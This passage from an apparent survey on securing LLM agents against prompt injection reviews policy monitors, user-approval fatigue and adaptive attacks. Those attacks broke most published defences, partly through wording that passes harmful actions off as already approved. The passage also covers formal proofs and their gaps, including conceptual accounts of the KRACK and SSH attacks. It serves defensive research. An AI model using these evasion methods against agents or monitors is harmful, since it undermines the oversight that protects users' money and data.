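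Experts leave gaps in policies too, as Yin did with password changes. When a simulated user rejected every request that showed the attacker's call, one of 909 AgentDojo attacks still succeeded against Trident with gpt-oss-120b. The injected text asked the agent to visit a web page, and the researchers' own root policy allowed that in any Slack task. The run obeyed the policy, so it did not contradict either theorem.

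Wang and colleagues are pessimistic about having a language model write the rules instead. They cite a recall of 70.96% for generated rules as evidence that nearly 30% of the necessary constraints are missing. The figure comes from *AgentSpec* (Wang, Poskitt and Sun, 2025), in which OpenAI's o1 model wrote rules for simulated household robots. It measures how the rules handled test cases, not what share of the necessary rules o1 wrote. The robots also did tasks like heating and pouring, not sending email or money.

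The original paper is also unclear about what its recall figure of 70.96% means. Recall is normally the share of risky cases that the rules catch, but the paper also says that the rules stopped 95.56% of risky cases, and both can't be right. Elsewhere it calls 95.56% the precision, which is normally the share of blocked cases that really were risky. The recall figure is therefore weak evidence about policies for tool-calling agents, especially since o1 is now an old model.

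The rules o1 generated for agents that write code caught 87.26% of risky programs. Some of the misses came from rules that protected the sensitive files named in the examples but not similar ones. For the household robots, a rule meant to stop them pouring liquids where they could do damage banned all pouring, even to water a houseplant. The code rules therefore made $A(P)$ too large, and the pouring rule made it too small. Wang, Poskitt and Sun recommend giving the model more precise requirements, but a person still has to specify what is safe.

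### The user's approval is part of the policy

If a rule requires asking the user, the policy also allows whatever the user approves, so the attack success rate depends on how carefully the user reads each request. *Trident* measures this at two extremes, using a new benchmark called ReplanInject, where part of the plan depends on untrusted content in 43 of the 45 tasks. When every request was approved, attacks succeeded in 3.4% to 4.8% of Trident's runs, depending on the model. When a simulated user rejected every request that showed the attacker's call, no attacks succeeded. Real users are probably somewhere in between.

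For Progent, the same two tests gave 7.0% to 41.8% and 5.8% to 11.9%. Careful review helps less with Progent, probably because users approve a rule that can later allow calls they never saw.

Real users also get tired. Wang and colleagues say that asking Claude Code to restructure a login system can trigger dozens of approval prompts, which they compare to browser security warnings that people click through without reading. Their argument rests on this analogy, not on measurements of people supervising agents. Willison mentions that even the security researcher Troy Hunt fell for a phishing attack while jet-lagged.

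The number of approval requests per task is a better guide to user fatigue than the share of policy updates that need approval, because a task can involve many updates. Shi and colleagues found that only 6% of Progent's policy updates needed approval and concluded that the burden on users is low. In *Trident*'s rerun of Progent on AgentDojo, however, users would have received between 1.06 and 1.62 requests per attacked run, compared with about half a request for Trident.

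Most requests are also legitimate, which makes the rare malicious one harder to notice. With GPT-4.1, Trident made 0.91 requests per attacked ReplanInject run, and 8.8% of those requests showed the attacker's call, or about 0.08 per run. If only one run in 1,000 contained an attack and the other runs produced requests at the same rate, the user would see about 11,000 requests for each one that showed an attack. It is very optimistic to assume that this user would reject every bad request.

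Even an attentive user can't always tell whether a request is safe to approve. Suppose someone tells an agent to do what Jane's email says, and the email asks for a payment to a new account. Jane may have written it, or an attacker may have sent the same text from her account. The monitor receives the same request, email and tool call either way, so any fixed rule must treat the two cases alike. Allowing the payment lets the attack succeed, while blocking it stops the agent from doing what the user asked when the email is really Jane's. Asking the user helps only if the user has information that the monitor lacks, for example from phoning Jane.

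ReplanInject contains three tasks of this kind. When every request was approved, attacks on them succeeded in 13.9% to 27.8% of Trident's runs. Garby and colleagues found the same problem in their own agent, which can mark selected untrusted values as trusted while it plans. Attacks succeeded in only two of its 1,296 attacked runs, both on a task that asked the agent to follow payment instructions in a file whose contents the attacker had replaced. Removing the agent's ability to trust such values blocks the attack but also prevents the agent from carrying out the legitimate request.

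### Narrow policies suit closed tasks

Many useful tasks don't need a flexible policy. If the user asks an agent to email Jane that they will be 15 minutes late, the request already names the action, the recipient and the content. A policy that allows only this email doesn't block anything the user asked for, and it is much easier to check than a policy that changes. A fixed policy also suits an agent that pays the same five suppliers every month. *Trident* reports that only 20 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks have a plan that depends on data the agent reads. Progent's initial policy, without later updates, cut the attack success rate on AgentDojo to 2.5%.

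The same approach works badly when the agent has to choose its actions based on the content it reads. With GPT-4.1, CaMeL completed 116 of 1,215 ReplanInject runs, too few to be of much use for this kind of work, though no attack succeeded. In 574 runs, its policy denied a call that contained nothing from the attacker, because the call depended on untrusted data. Trident completed 54% to 74% of attacked runs, but with GPT-4.1, a Trident run cost nearly four times as much as a Progent run.

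Letting users approve exceptions can recover some of the lost work, but it weakens the original guarantee. With Claude Sonnet 4.5, FIDES completed 3.3% of attacked ReplanInject runs under its strict policy and 75.2% with approvals, more than Trident's 64.4%. But in 90% of the runs with approvals, FIDES's planner read free text derived from untrusted data, and after that the user's review was the only check. When every request was approved, 6.0% of attacks succeeded, compared with none under the strict policy.

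## What if the attacker adapts to the defence?

An attack success rate depends on the attacker as well as the defence. Suppose one forger sends the invoice agent a single email copied from a public collection of prompt injections. Another forger has a copy of the agent, tries a thousand versions of the email on it and sends the one that worked most often. With the same defence, the agent might ignore the first forger's email and pay the second forger.

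Attackers differ mainly in what they know about the defence, how many attempts they get, how much computing power they have and whether skilled people take part. Every measured rate depends on assumptions about all four. If researchers test a defence only on attacks written before it existed, the result holds only if real attackers do no better than those attacks.

### The precedent from image classifiers

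Researchers working on image classifiers ran into this problem first. An attacker can often make a classifier mislabel an image by changing it slightly, and many papers reported defences that were highly robust against fixed attacks of this kind. *AutoDojo* recounts that Athalye, Carlini and Wagner broke such defences in 2018 by adapting the attacks to them, and that in 2020 Tramèr and colleagues broke thirteen defences whose designers had already tested them with adaptive attacks. So reporting that a defence was tested against an adaptive attack isn't enough, because the attack may have been weak.

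*The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025; later published at the USENIX Security conference) argues that research on language models has overlooked this history. Researchers test most new defences against either a fixed list of old attacks or a general-purpose attack program that nobody has adjusted to the defence. Defences are also harder to test on text than on images. Against an image classifier, a program that needs little computation can calculate how each small change affects the output, and it finds attacks more reliably than any person. No program is that reliable for text, and skilled people still often do better. A failed automatic attack is therefore weaker evidence of security for a language model than for an image classifier.

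### Twelve defences tested again

Nasr and colleagues attacked 12 published defences. The original papers had reported attack success rates near zero for most of them. Some defend against prompt injection and others against jailbreaks, in which the user tries to make the model break its own rules. The defences add instructions to the prompt, train the model on known attacks, filter text with a separate classifier, or rely on a secret the attacker is assumed not to know.

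Each attack repeats a loop in which the attacker proposes a text, scores how close it came to succeeding, keeps the best attempts and revises them. The first version uses reinforcement learning to train a model to write the attacks. The second uses a language model to rewrite the most promising earlier attempts. The third uses gradients, as in the attacks on image classifiers, and the fourth relies on people. For each defence, the researchers chose the methods they thought most likely to work.

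This table shows the results on 80 AgentDojo scenarios, with Gemini 2.5 Pro as the agent's model. The last column covers the benchmark's full set of ordinary tasks.

| Defence | Fixed attack succeeds | Adaptive search succeeds | Tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 30% | 100% | 74% |
| Spotlighting (marks which text is trusted) | 28% | 99% | 75% |
| Prompt sandwiching (repeats the user's request) | 21% | 95% | 73% |
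| PromptGuard (filter) | 26% | 94% | 72% |
| Protect AI (filter) | 15% | 90% | 39% |
| Model Armor (filter) | 28% | 90% | 59% |
| PIGuard (filter) | 0% | 71% | 39% |
| MELON (secret second run) | 0% | 89% | 58% |

The other five defences did no better. MetaSecAlign, a model trained to resist injection, had a reported attack success rate of 2% on AgentDojo, which rose to 96% under adaptive attacks. Attacks succeeded every time against StruQ and Circuit Breakers, which also rely on training, and 98% of the time against RPO, an optimised prompt meant to prevent jailbreaks. Data Sentinel, another defence with a secret test, was reported to miss almost no attacks, but the researchers bypassed it every time.

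Success is measured differently in the two attack columns. The fixed attack uses one prepared text, while the search could make up to 800 tries in each scenario and counts as successful if any of them worked. Some of the increase therefore comes from the extra tries, but where the search succeeded against Gemini 2.5 Pro, the median number of tries was only 13 to 46, depending on the defence.

With GPT-5 Mini, the fixed attack never succeeded even without a defence, so anyone testing these defences on that model could have reported a 0% attack success rate. The search succeeded in 75% of scenarios without a defence and in 47% to 81% with one. Spotlighting (47%) and PIGuard (49%) probably helped somewhat, but far less than a 0% rate would suggest.

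MELON runs the model a second time on a harmless dummy task and treats a tool call that appears in both runs as a sign of injection. With Llama 3.3 70B, the search succeeded in 76% of scenarios when given no information about MELON, and in 95% when told how it works. Security researchers have assumed since Kerckhoffs in 1883 that the attacker knows the design, and by that standard only the 95% figure counts.

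To test attacks by people, Nasr and colleagues held a contest with more than 500 participants and $20,000 in prizes. Together, the participants beat every challenge. On the 29 scenarios that both people and the search attempted, people collectively succeeded in all 29 and the search in 69%. But this compares hundreds of people with one run of a program. Only three people tried all 29 scenarios. The best succeeded in 75%, and the other two did worse than the search.

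A low success rate per attempt gave little protection in this contest. In one scenario with Gemini 2.5 Pro, MELON cut the success rate of submissions from 11.1% to 0.4%, but at least one attacker still got through.

Automatic attackers can also make a defence look worse than it is. Against StruQ, one such attacker learned to raise its score by exploiting the scoring formula without defeating the defence. Nasr and colleagues therefore checked the successful attacks by hand.

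### What knowledge and repetition add

*Adaptive Attacks Break Defenses Against Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks on LLM Agents* (Zhan, Fang and colleagues, 2025) tested eight defences for agents, including detectors, warnings in the prompt and extra training. The attacker had full access to the agent's model and the defence, and succeeded more than half the time against each one.

For two of the defences, the study also measured the effect of adapting an attack to the defence separately from the effect of optimising it. One of these defences paraphrases outside text before the agent reads it, which disrupts attacks that depend on exact wording. When a Llama 3 8B agent used this defence, attacks optimised against an undefended agent succeeded 8% of the time, while attacks optimised with the paraphrasing in mind succeeded 54% of the time. The study used 100 test cases and two small models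 that are now very old, so these rates are weak evidence about current agents, but the gap between them is more informative.

*Adaptive Adversaries* (Jain, Hartmann and Li, 2026), a benchmark presented at the machine-learning conference ICML, used newer models. Claude Opus 4.6, GPT-5.4 and Gemini 2.5 Pro each played both attacker and defender in 21 scenarios. The attacker had up to 15 rounds and saw the defender's earlier answers, while the defender started afresh each round. In the first round, attacks succeeded 0% to 1% of the time, depending on the defender. Within 15 rounds, they succeeded 7.9% of the time against Opus, 9.5% against GPT-5.4 and 16.8% against Gemini, and the rates were still rising.

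This increase came largely from learning. In a follow-up on three scenarios, attackers who could see their earlier attempts won 13 of 36 contests, while those who had the same 15 tries but could not see earlier attempts won none. Memory also helped the defender in another test, where attackers won 57% of contests against a defender that forgot earlier rounds and 31% against one that remembered them.

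The first-round result was near zero partly because Jain and colleagues revised the scenarios so that attacks could emerge over several rounds. The defenders also had no real tools, and code checked only what they wrote. When the researchers replayed successful attacks, 67% worked again on the same model but only 12% on a different one. Testing a new model with attacks collected from older ones may therefore greatly underestimate what the same attackers could do to it.

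An attacker can also succeed more often by trying repeatedly. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) quotes Anthropic's results for Claude Opus 4.5, which Anthropic has since replaced, against an automated attacker. The attack success rate was 4.7% after one attempt, 33.6% after ten and 63.0% after a hundred. If the attempts had been independent, the rate would have reached 38% after ten and 99% after a hundred.

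The US government's Center for AI Standards and Innovation (CAISI) found a similar pattern with a model from October 2024. Its *Strengthening AI Agent Hijacking Evaluations* (2025) reports that the average success rate across five attack goals rose from 57% with one attempt to 80% with 25. If every goal had a 57% chance on each attempt, at least one of 25 independent attempts would almost always succeed.

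This is probably because some goals are much harder than others. Repeated attempts soon succeed on the easy ones but may never succeed on the hard ones. Researchers therefore have to measure the success rate for many attempts, since they can't calculate it from the rate for one. In the same study, tailoring the attack to the model made a larger difference than repeating it. The strongest existing attack succeeded 11% of the time, and the strongest new one 81%, on user tasks that the new attack's developers had not used.

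*How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) reports on another public contest, in which 464 people made about 272,000 attempts against 13 models. Attacks succeeded against every model, at rates from 0.5% of attempts for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Gemini 2.5 Pro. Successes kept growing roughly in proportion to attempts, so the participants showed no sign of running out of attacks that worked.

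Claude Opus 4.5's attack success rate was therefore 0.5% in this contest and 4.7% on the automated attacker's first attempt. The two tests used different scenarios, the contest's participants varied widely in skill, and most of their attacks also had to leave no trace in the agent's final reply. An attack success rate only has meaning for a particular kind of attacker and task, so neither figure is the model's true rate.

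### Defences outside the model

Nasr and colleagues broke 12 defences, all of which try either to make the model resist an attack or to recognise one. They left out designs such as CaMeL, which plan before reading untrusted text, because most attacks in their scenarios would inevitably have failed. The researchers, five of whom had also worked on CaMeL, recommend testing such designs on tasks where the plan depends on what the agent reads, as Trident's benchmark later did.

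Defenders of these designs reply that a check outside the model does not depend on how an attacker words the attack. Such a check computes a decision

$$D(a, \ell, P) \in \{\text{allow}, \text{block}\}$$

from the proposed call $a$, the labels $\ell$ on its data and the policy $P$. The attacker's text is not an input. It can change which call the model proposes, but if it cannot change $\ell$ or $P$, no rewording will get a forbidden call through. Once the payee list is in place, a thousand versions of the forged invoice do no better than one at sending money to a new account.

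Recent papers state this position in their threat models. *Kairos* (2026) assumes an adaptive attacker who knows the design and the operator's policy but cannot reach the monitor or the machine it runs on. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) assumes nothing about how the model reasons. *Agenra* (2026) aims to block forbidden calls even if the agent proposes them deliberately.

The argument is sound, but it covers only calls that the policy forbids. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* excludes from its scope any unsafe action that the policy allows, and *Agenra* notes that a monitor cannot enforce a missing rule. An attacker who knows the policy can look for unsafe actions that it allows, such as a repeat payment to an approved supplier.

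Wording also matters if a language model helps to set $\ell$ or $P$, or makes part of the decision. *AutoDojo* provides some evidence. Its attacker doesn't know which defence is in place, sees only whether each attempt succeeded, and gets six rounds of revision. Against a GPT-4o-mini agent, it raised the success rate from 0% to 28% for the PIGuard filter, and from 2.6% to 6.4% for DRIFT, which restricts the agent's actions but uses a language model to judge some of them. The rate did not rise for Progent, although 7.7% of attacks still succeeded. The paper describes CaMeL and ROPE, which track where data came from, as immune to rewording whenever their policies are correct. Some of its authors also built ROPE.

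These results fit the defenders' argument but are a weak test of it, because *AutoDojo*'s attacker can only rewrite text, which a well-built check ignores. An attacker who targeted the labels, the policy or the person approving requests might do better.

The defences also made agents complete fewer ordinary tasks. DRIFT lowered the share completed by 18 percentage points with GPT-4o-mini, and CaMeL caused the largest drop on four of the five models. On AgentDyn, a benchmark with more open-ended tasks, agents protected by Progent completed fewer than 7% of tasks, compared with 37% to 47% for undefended agents.

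### An adaptive test of Progent

Narisetty and colleagues argue that defences outside the model have mostly faced only fixed attacks, as had the defences that later broke. They tested Progent, a defence outside the model, against an attacker who knows how it works. The Progent paper had already reported a test of this kind with GPT-4o, in which attacks succeeded about 0.5% to 4.2% of the time. The new test used a much weaker model, Qwen2.5-7B, both to run the agent and to write Progent's policies.

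The adaptive attack targeted the language model that updates the policy. It tried to get the model to permit the harmful action by presenting it as a normal, already approved part of the task. The researchers ran eight user tasks from each of three AgentDojo suites, combined them with every attack goal, and repeated the test three times.

| Suite | No defence, standard attack | Progent, standard attack | Progent, adaptive attack |
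|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 19.0% | 1.9% | 3.7% |
| Slack | 58.3% | 10.8% | 4.2% |
| Workspace | 0% | 0% | 0% |
| Mean | 25.8% | 4.2% | 2.6% |

Progent clearly stopped most of the standard attacks. Whether it withstood an adaptive attacker is much less clear, because the adaptive attack succeeded less often overall than the standard one. Narisetty and colleagues suggest that the adaptive attack's gentler wording made the agent itself less likely to obey. They did not run that attack on an undefended agent, which would have tested this explanation. As they acknowledge, the low success rate could reflect a weak attack as much as a strong defence. The researchers work for LaunchSafe, which builds security tools of this kind.

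Progent also reduced the share of tasks completed under attack from 45% to 27% and needed about 15 times as many model calls per task.

The researchers describe a stronger test in which the attacker would try to forge the source of data, persuade users to approve harmful requests, probe for side channels like those in CaMeL, and pursue the goal using only tools that the policy already allows. Each of these methods targets a condition of the guarantee instead of trying to get a forbidden call past the check. Nobody has yet run such a test across several of these defences.

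Even a monitor that passed this test would leave the gaps already described: tasks where untrusted text has to determine an action, wrong labels on incoming data, and replies that mislead the user.

### Twin Agent's bet on short messages

Researchers sometimes call a design secure when its protection still depends on how a model behaves. *Twin Agent* (Hu, Jacob and colleagues, 2026) splits an agent into an Explore Agent, which reads untrusted text but cannot take privileged actions, and a Safe Agent, which can take those actions but never sees that text. At each step, the Explore Agent may send the Safe Agent a short hint, which a detector checks for signs of injection. Hints were limited to 100 characters in the tests on software bugs.

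The design works well against fixed attacks. On bug-fixing tasks with instructions planted in the bug reports, attacks succeeded 97% of the time against an undefended GPT-5.2 agent and never against Twin Agent, which fixed about as many bugs. On AgentDojo, Twin Agent completed twice as many tasks as CaMeL, and 0.1% of attacks against it succeeded.

Hu and colleagues call Twin Agent "secure-by-design", but they also say that this depends on an assumption. They believe it is hard to find a short injection that both gets past the detector and controls a frontier model. Software can enforce the 100-character limit exactly, but only experiments can show whether 100 characters are too few to attack current models.

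The limit is also looser than Trident's. A message of 100 printable characters can carry up to about 650 bits, and the Explore Agent can send one at every step. Trident suggests influence budgets of 39 to 88 bits for a whole run. Its planner receives only answers from a fixed list, so an answer cannot contain an instruction that the attacker wrote.

To test the assumption, Hu and colleagues optimised short malicious hints against the Safe Agent. None made it take the harmful action in its next step. They then found that an attacker could always make the Explore Agent pass on such a hint. When they combined the two attacks and let the agent finish the whole task, at least one malicious hint got past the detector in 57 of 232 runs, and the harmful action occurred in 11 (4.7%). The single-step test had missed these harmful actions because a full run gives the attacker many chances.

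Hu and colleagues reran the 11 failed cases five times each, and none failed again. They conclude that the failures were random, though they accept that any successful attack is a security failure. But 55 reruns are too few to show that the failure rate is below 4.7%, because even at that rate there would be about a 7% chance of seeing no failures. If the failures are random, no case is permanently safe, so repeated attempts are especially useful to the attacker. At a 4.7% rate, an attacker who filed 15 malicious bug reports would have about an even chance that at least one worked.

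Shorter hints make attacks harder, but they also give the Safe Agent less help fixing the bug. The right length also depends on the model, so a deployer who replaces GPT-5.2 would have to repeat the adaptive test. A monitor that stopped the Safe Agent from deleting files would block one of the two harmful actions in this experiment, whatever the hint said.

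## What does a security proof leave open?

A proof can cover attacks that nobody has thought of, which no test against an adaptive attacker can do. But attackers have broken systems that came with proofs. In the three cases below, all older than today's AI agents, mistakes in the mathematics did not cause the failures.

### Wi-Fi devices installed the same key twice

When a laptop joins a Wi-Fi network protected by the WPA2 standard, the laptop and router exchange four messages, called the four-way handshake. Each side sends a random number, and both combine the two numbers with a secret they already share, such as the Wi-Fi password, to make a fresh encryption key. When the third message arrives, the laptop installs the key, meaning it starts encrypting with it, and confirms this in the fourth message.

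*A Modular Correctness Proof of IEEE 802.11i and TLS* (He, Sundararajan and colleagues, 2005) proved that the Wi-Fi handshake keeps the key secret and that each side is really talking to the other. *Key Reinstallation Attacks* (Vanhoef, 2017) reports that other researchers had proved the encryption itself secure, and that for over a decade nobody found an attack on the handshake except guessing the password.

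Then Vanhoef and Piessens discovered the key reinstallation attack, or KRACK. WPA2 encrypts each packet by combining it with a keystream $S(k,n)$, a string of bits computed from the key $k$ and a packet number $n$. If two packets $p_1$ and $p_2$ use the same keystream, it cancels out when an attacker combines their encrypted versions:

$$c_1 \oplus c_2 = (p_1 \oplus S(k,n)) \oplus (p_2 \oplus S(k,n)) = p_1 \oplus p_2$$

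An attacker who knows the contents of one packet can then work out the other. To prevent this, the laptop sets $n$ to zero when it installs the key and increases it with every packet. But radio messages sometimes get lost, so the router resends the third message if it receives no confirmation. An attacker within range can block the confirmation, and when the router resends the message, the laptop reinstalls the same key, resets $n$ to zero and reuses the old keystream.

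The proof is still correct, because the attacker never learns the negotiated key and cannot impersonate either side. But it does not address how often a device may install the key. In *A Formal Analysis of IEEE 802.11's WPA2*, Cremers, Kiesl and Medinger (2020) found three simplifications in the 2005 analysis, any one of which would have hidden KRACK. The analysis left out the properties of the encryption. It included only one of the protocol's counters and assumed that this counter always increases, which is false for some devices that follow the standard. It also modeled the handshake as a fixed sequence of steps, without the branches that let a device reset its counters. Yet He and colleagues write in their abstract that the proof holds for "a variety of failure recovery strategies", which a reader could easily take to include resending lost messages.

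The first repairs failed too. Vanhoef and Piessens argued informally that their countermeasures would work, and the standards body IEEE adopted a slightly different one. In 2018, the two researchers got around both. Cremers and colleagues then built a model that included encryption, resent messages and a power-saving mode that the newer attacks had used. Without the patches, the model reproduced KRACK. With two of the patches, they could prove that the keys stay secret. One stops a device from resetting the packet number of a key that is already installed, and the other makes it delete the broadcast key before going to sleep. The proof doesn't cover side channels or mistakes in particular Wi-Fi chips, and Cremers and colleagues could not rule out that a device might reinstall a broadcast key.

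### SSH revealed the length of a packet

SSH is the usual way to log in to a remote computer. *Breaking and Provably Repairing the SSH Authenticated Encryption Scheme* (Bellare, Kohno and Namprempre, 2002) identified a weakness in SSH's encryption and proved that several modified versions were secure, even against an attacker who can send altered messages and have them decrypted. *Plaintext Recovery Attacks Against SSH* (Albrecht, Paterson and Watson, 2009) described an attack that works on the original protocol and on one of the versions with a proof.

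SSH encrypts data in blocks, and the encrypted data includes each packet's length, in its first 32 bits. The server therefore has to decrypt the first block to determine how much data to wait for. It can check whether the packet is genuine only after all the data has arrived. This lets an attacker record an encrypted block from somebody's session and send it as the start of a new packet. The server decrypts the block and reads the first 32 bits as a length. The attacker then sends random data, one block at a time, until the server reports an error, and works out the 32 bits from the amount of data needed.

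These are not quite the user's original bits, because the encryption mode, called CBC, mixes each block with the one before it. If $D$ is the decryption function, the original text of block $c_i$ is $p_i = c_{i-1} \oplus D(c_i)$. When the attacker sends $c_i$ after a different block $c'$, the server gets $p' = c' \oplus D(c_i)$ instead. But the attacker has seen all the encrypted blocks and can convert one into the other:

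$$p_i = p' \oplus c' \oplus c_{i-1}$$

OpenSSH, the most common implementation, rejected implausible lengths, which reduced the chance of recovering 32 bits to about one in 262,000 per attempt. Each attempt also broke the connection. The attack was therefore a serious threat mainly to data that a program resends on every new connection, such as a password, but the proof should still have ruled it out.

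The SSH proof by Bellare and his co-authors didn't fully cover real servers because the attacker in its model learned only that decryption had failed. A real server also revealed how it had failed and how much data it had received first. In an Internet draft for people implementing SSH, they had written that the modified protocol "provably preserves privacy and integrity", even against attackers who watch how the server reacts, but that sentence didn't specify which reactions the model included. Paterson and Watson (2010), in *Plaintext-Dependent Decryption*, repaired the analysis with a model in which the amount of data depends on the decrypted length, and proved security for SSH with a different encryption mode.

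### Sixteen bugs around verified code

The Wi-Fi and SSH proofs were about descriptions of protocols. A proof about the code itself should leave fewer gaps, but it can still leave some. Fonseca, Zhang and colleagues (2017), in *An Empirical Study on the Correctness of Formally Verified Distributed Systems*, found 16 bugs when they examined IronFleet, Verdi and Chapar, three research systems that have machine-checked proofs about their code and keep copies of data consistent across several servers.

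Eleven bugs involved the shim layer, the unverified code that connects the verified part to the network and the disk. Nine of these made servers crash or hang. Verdi, for example, treated each read from the network as a whole request, so it crashed when a request arrived in pieces. It also used spaces and line breaks to separate commands without checking whether a client's data contained them, so a client could hide a second command inside the first. Prompt injection also exploits a failure to separate data from instructions.

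Three more bugs were in the tools that check the proofs, and two of these could make IronFleet's tool accept an incorrect program. The last two were in specifications, the formal statements of what a system should do. IronFleet's specification did not require the server to carry out each request exactly once. The server did so anyway, but when Fonseca and colleagues changed seven lines to disable this feature, the program still passed verification. In a bank, that change could turn a repeated network message into a repeated payment. The developers replied that they had known about the omission and did not consider exactly-once execution part of the property they were proving. They added a comment saying so to the code.

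Fonseca and colleagues searched for more than eight months and found no mistakes in the protocols, which are notoriously hard to implement. IronFleet, which had the least unverified code, had no bugs in its shim layer. Most of the bugs were in a few hundred lines around the verified parts, so the researchers built a set of tests for those lines. The tests detect 13 of the 16 bugs.

### Four different faults

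These cases involve four kinds of fault, each of which needs a different check.

| Fault | Example | How to look for it |
|---|---|---|
| The proof is wrong | IronFleet's tool could accept an incorrect program | Use a small proof checker and test it on programs that should fail |
| The model omits part of the system | The SSH model had only one kind of error | Compare the model with the running system, step by step |
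| An assumption is false in deployment | Verdi assumed that requests arrive whole | Test the assumption where the system will run |
| A summary drops the conditions | The SSH draft said "provably" without describing the model | Compare the summary with the theorem |

Omissions are the hardest gaps for a deployer to deal with, because people can test the assumptions a paper lists but not a condition the researchers never thought to write down. People often find omissions while reading the code for another reason. Vanhoef was finishing a different paper when he noticed the function that installs a Wi-Fi key and wondered what would happen if a device called it twice.

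A specification can have omissions too. IronFleet's proof was correct for the property its developers chose, but a user who expected each request to run only once was relying on an unproved property.

### The dispute over provable security

The best-known critics of security proofs are the cryptographers Koblitz and Menezes. *Fundamental Challenges in Cybersecurity and a Philosophy of Vulnerability-Guided Hardening* (Böhme, 2024) summarises their criticism as an objection to people advertising these guarantees as final. Their examples from cryptography include incorrect proofs, idealised models, broken assumptions and inadequate definitions. Herley and van Oorschot go further and argue that nobody can prove that a real system will withstand every attack, because a proof is about a mathematical object and the system is a physical one. De Millo, Lipton and Perlis objected to program verification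 for a different reason. They argued that mathematicians come to trust a theorem because many other people study it, and predicted that program verification would fail because nobody would study proofs about programs in that way.

The critics are right that a proof is not final, but the same cases are also good evidence for proofs. The Wi-Fi patches that rested on an informal argument failed within about a year, and a formal model was needed to show which patches were enough. The formal analysis of SSH missed one weakness, but it had already found another in the original protocol. Fonseca and colleagues found many protocol bugs among the known bugs in mature distributed systems without proofs, and none in the verified systems.

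Böhme accepts most of the criticism but still regards a proof as a guarantee under stated assumptions. Böhme advises researchers to treat an attack that succeeds despite a proof as a counterexample and extend the model to include it, as they did for Wi-Fi and SSH. This is sensible advice, but extending the model can be slow. Fifteen years passed between the first Wi-Fi proof and one that could detect KRACK.

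### What the proof about prompt injection covers

Dongol's proof about prompt injection dates from November 2026, so other researchers have had little time to look for counterexamples. The proof checker Isabelle/HOL has verified it, which makes a mathematical mistake very unlikely. The main open questions are therefore about the property it proves and the model it uses.

Relative security compares the agent with a reference agent that ignores injected instructions. A pair of secrets leaks if an attacker who behaves identically in two runs can observe a difference between them. The agent is relatively secure if, for every pair of secrets $s_1$ and $s_2$,

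$$\text{the agent leaks } (s_1, s_2) \;\Rightarrow\; \text{the reference agent leaks } (s_1, s_2)$$

An agent can be relatively secure and still reveal more to an attacker than a genuine request would. Suppose an agent's job is to tell anyone who asks whether a guess at the user's PIN is correct. For any two PINs, some guess distinguishes them, so the reference agent counts as leaking the difference between every pair. An agent that follows an injected instruction to send the attacker the whole PIN therefore still counts as relatively secure, although a genuine request reveals only whether one guess is right. Dongol describes a similar case and defines a stricter version of the property, in which the attacker's input to the reference agent may not depend on the secret.

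The result also depends on what the attacker can observe. In one example, Alice approves an email reply before the agent sends it. If her approval covers any use of the email tool, an injected instruction can make the agent email her private data to the attacker. If it covers only the exact reply, the agent is relatively secure against an attacker who sees only the messages. But if the private data is identical to the approved reply, an injected request to send that data will go through, and the reply will leave one step early. An attacker who can time the agent's steps can therefore learn whether the two are identical.

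Dongol lists several exclusions at the start of the paper. The largest is agents whose model chooses every call, as coding agents usually do. They are excluded because they have no fixed plan for a reference agent to follow. Dongol also excludes poisoned tools, multi-agent systems, side channels, planner mistakes, and tools whose replies depend on the query, such as a search engine run by the attacker. For the invoice agent, the most important exclusion remains an injected payment that leaks no data.

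The paper gives verdicts for 25 small example agents. Dongol calls them litmus tests and does not present them as a sample of real applications. Someone who read only that a computer had checked a proof about prompt injection might expect the proof to cover the agent on their laptop.

### PerMIT turns every attack into one decision

*PerMIT*, the design for protecting an agent's long-term memory, has two main theorems. Action Integrity states that every value reaching a sensitive tool is one that the user typed or one that somebody confirmed, character for character, for that tool. Reasoning Integrity compares two runs, $\rho_1$ and $\rho_2$, that differ only in their untrusted content:

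$$\mathrm{DT}(\rho_1) = \mathrm{DT}(\rho_2) \;\Rightarrow\; \mathrm{Beh}(\rho_1) = \mathrm{Beh}(\rho_2)$$

Here $\mathrm{DT}$ is everything the confirmation gate displayed and the decisions made there, and $\mathrm{Beh}$ is the agent's behavior. An attacker can therefore influence the agent only through what appears at the gate.

Neither theorem guarantees that the decisions are right. If the gate displays the forged invoice's account number and the user accepts it, both theorems hold and the attacker gets the money. A confirmation also covers less than a user might assume, because it applies only to a value and a tool, not to the task, the time or the other values in the call. Suppose the user has confirmed a $4,000 payment to a landlord and a $40 payment to a new supplier. Action Integrity would permit a $4,000 payment to the supplier, because the user has confirmed both that amount and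 that recipient for the bank tool.

*PerMIT* is unusually open about such limits. It includes a ledger of assumptions, an index of attacks and limitations, and a list of differences between the written model and the one checked by Lean, the proof checker also used in *Trident* and by David and colleagues. These show that the computer-checked proof covers only the core of the system for a single user. The Lean files are available only on request until the paper is published, so most readers have to take the proof on trust.

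The least certain conditions are in the parts that the Lean proof does not cover. A language model can make the decisions at the gate, and *PerMIT* reports no successful attacks on a memory benchmark with this setup. This is a measured result, and an attacker can still try to word an entry so that the verifiers accept it. In the version for communities, an item needs no further confirmation once enough users have confirmed it. A proof on paper shows that, under stated assumptions, the risk of accepting a poisoned item falls as the community grows, and a simulation gives the same result. But a simulation cannot establish that real verifiers behave as assumed. If many agents run on the same model, for example, one well-worded item might get past them all.

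### Testing a guardrail called provably secure

Wu, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Provably Secure Agent Guardrail*, propose a monitor that checks each action with a solver. The agent has to write its proposed action $j$ in a fixed format, and ordinary code translates this into a logical formula $[\![j]\!]$. The solver then looks for a way to make three things true at once:

$$s \wedge [\![j]\!] \wedge \Phi$$

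where $s$ is the current state and $\Phi$ is the set of safety rules. If it finds one, the action runs. If the three contradict each other, the monitor blocks it. Wu and colleagues prove that the system never reaches a state that breaks the rules, even if the model is hostile.

The formula comes from the action that will run, so the model can't submit a harmless description and then do something else. Because the monitor tracks the state, it can also catch an attacker who splits a large transfer into small ones to stay under a limit, which the payee list could not do.

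The theorem depends heavily on an assumption called Structured Intent Fidelity. The paper explains why it needs this assumption but doesn't state exactly what must be true. The proof uses it to conclude that running the action does what the formula describes and has no other effects, which is close to assuming the hardest part of the result. A bank tool would violate the assumption if it also saved the recipient for future payments or charged a fee on top of the amount.

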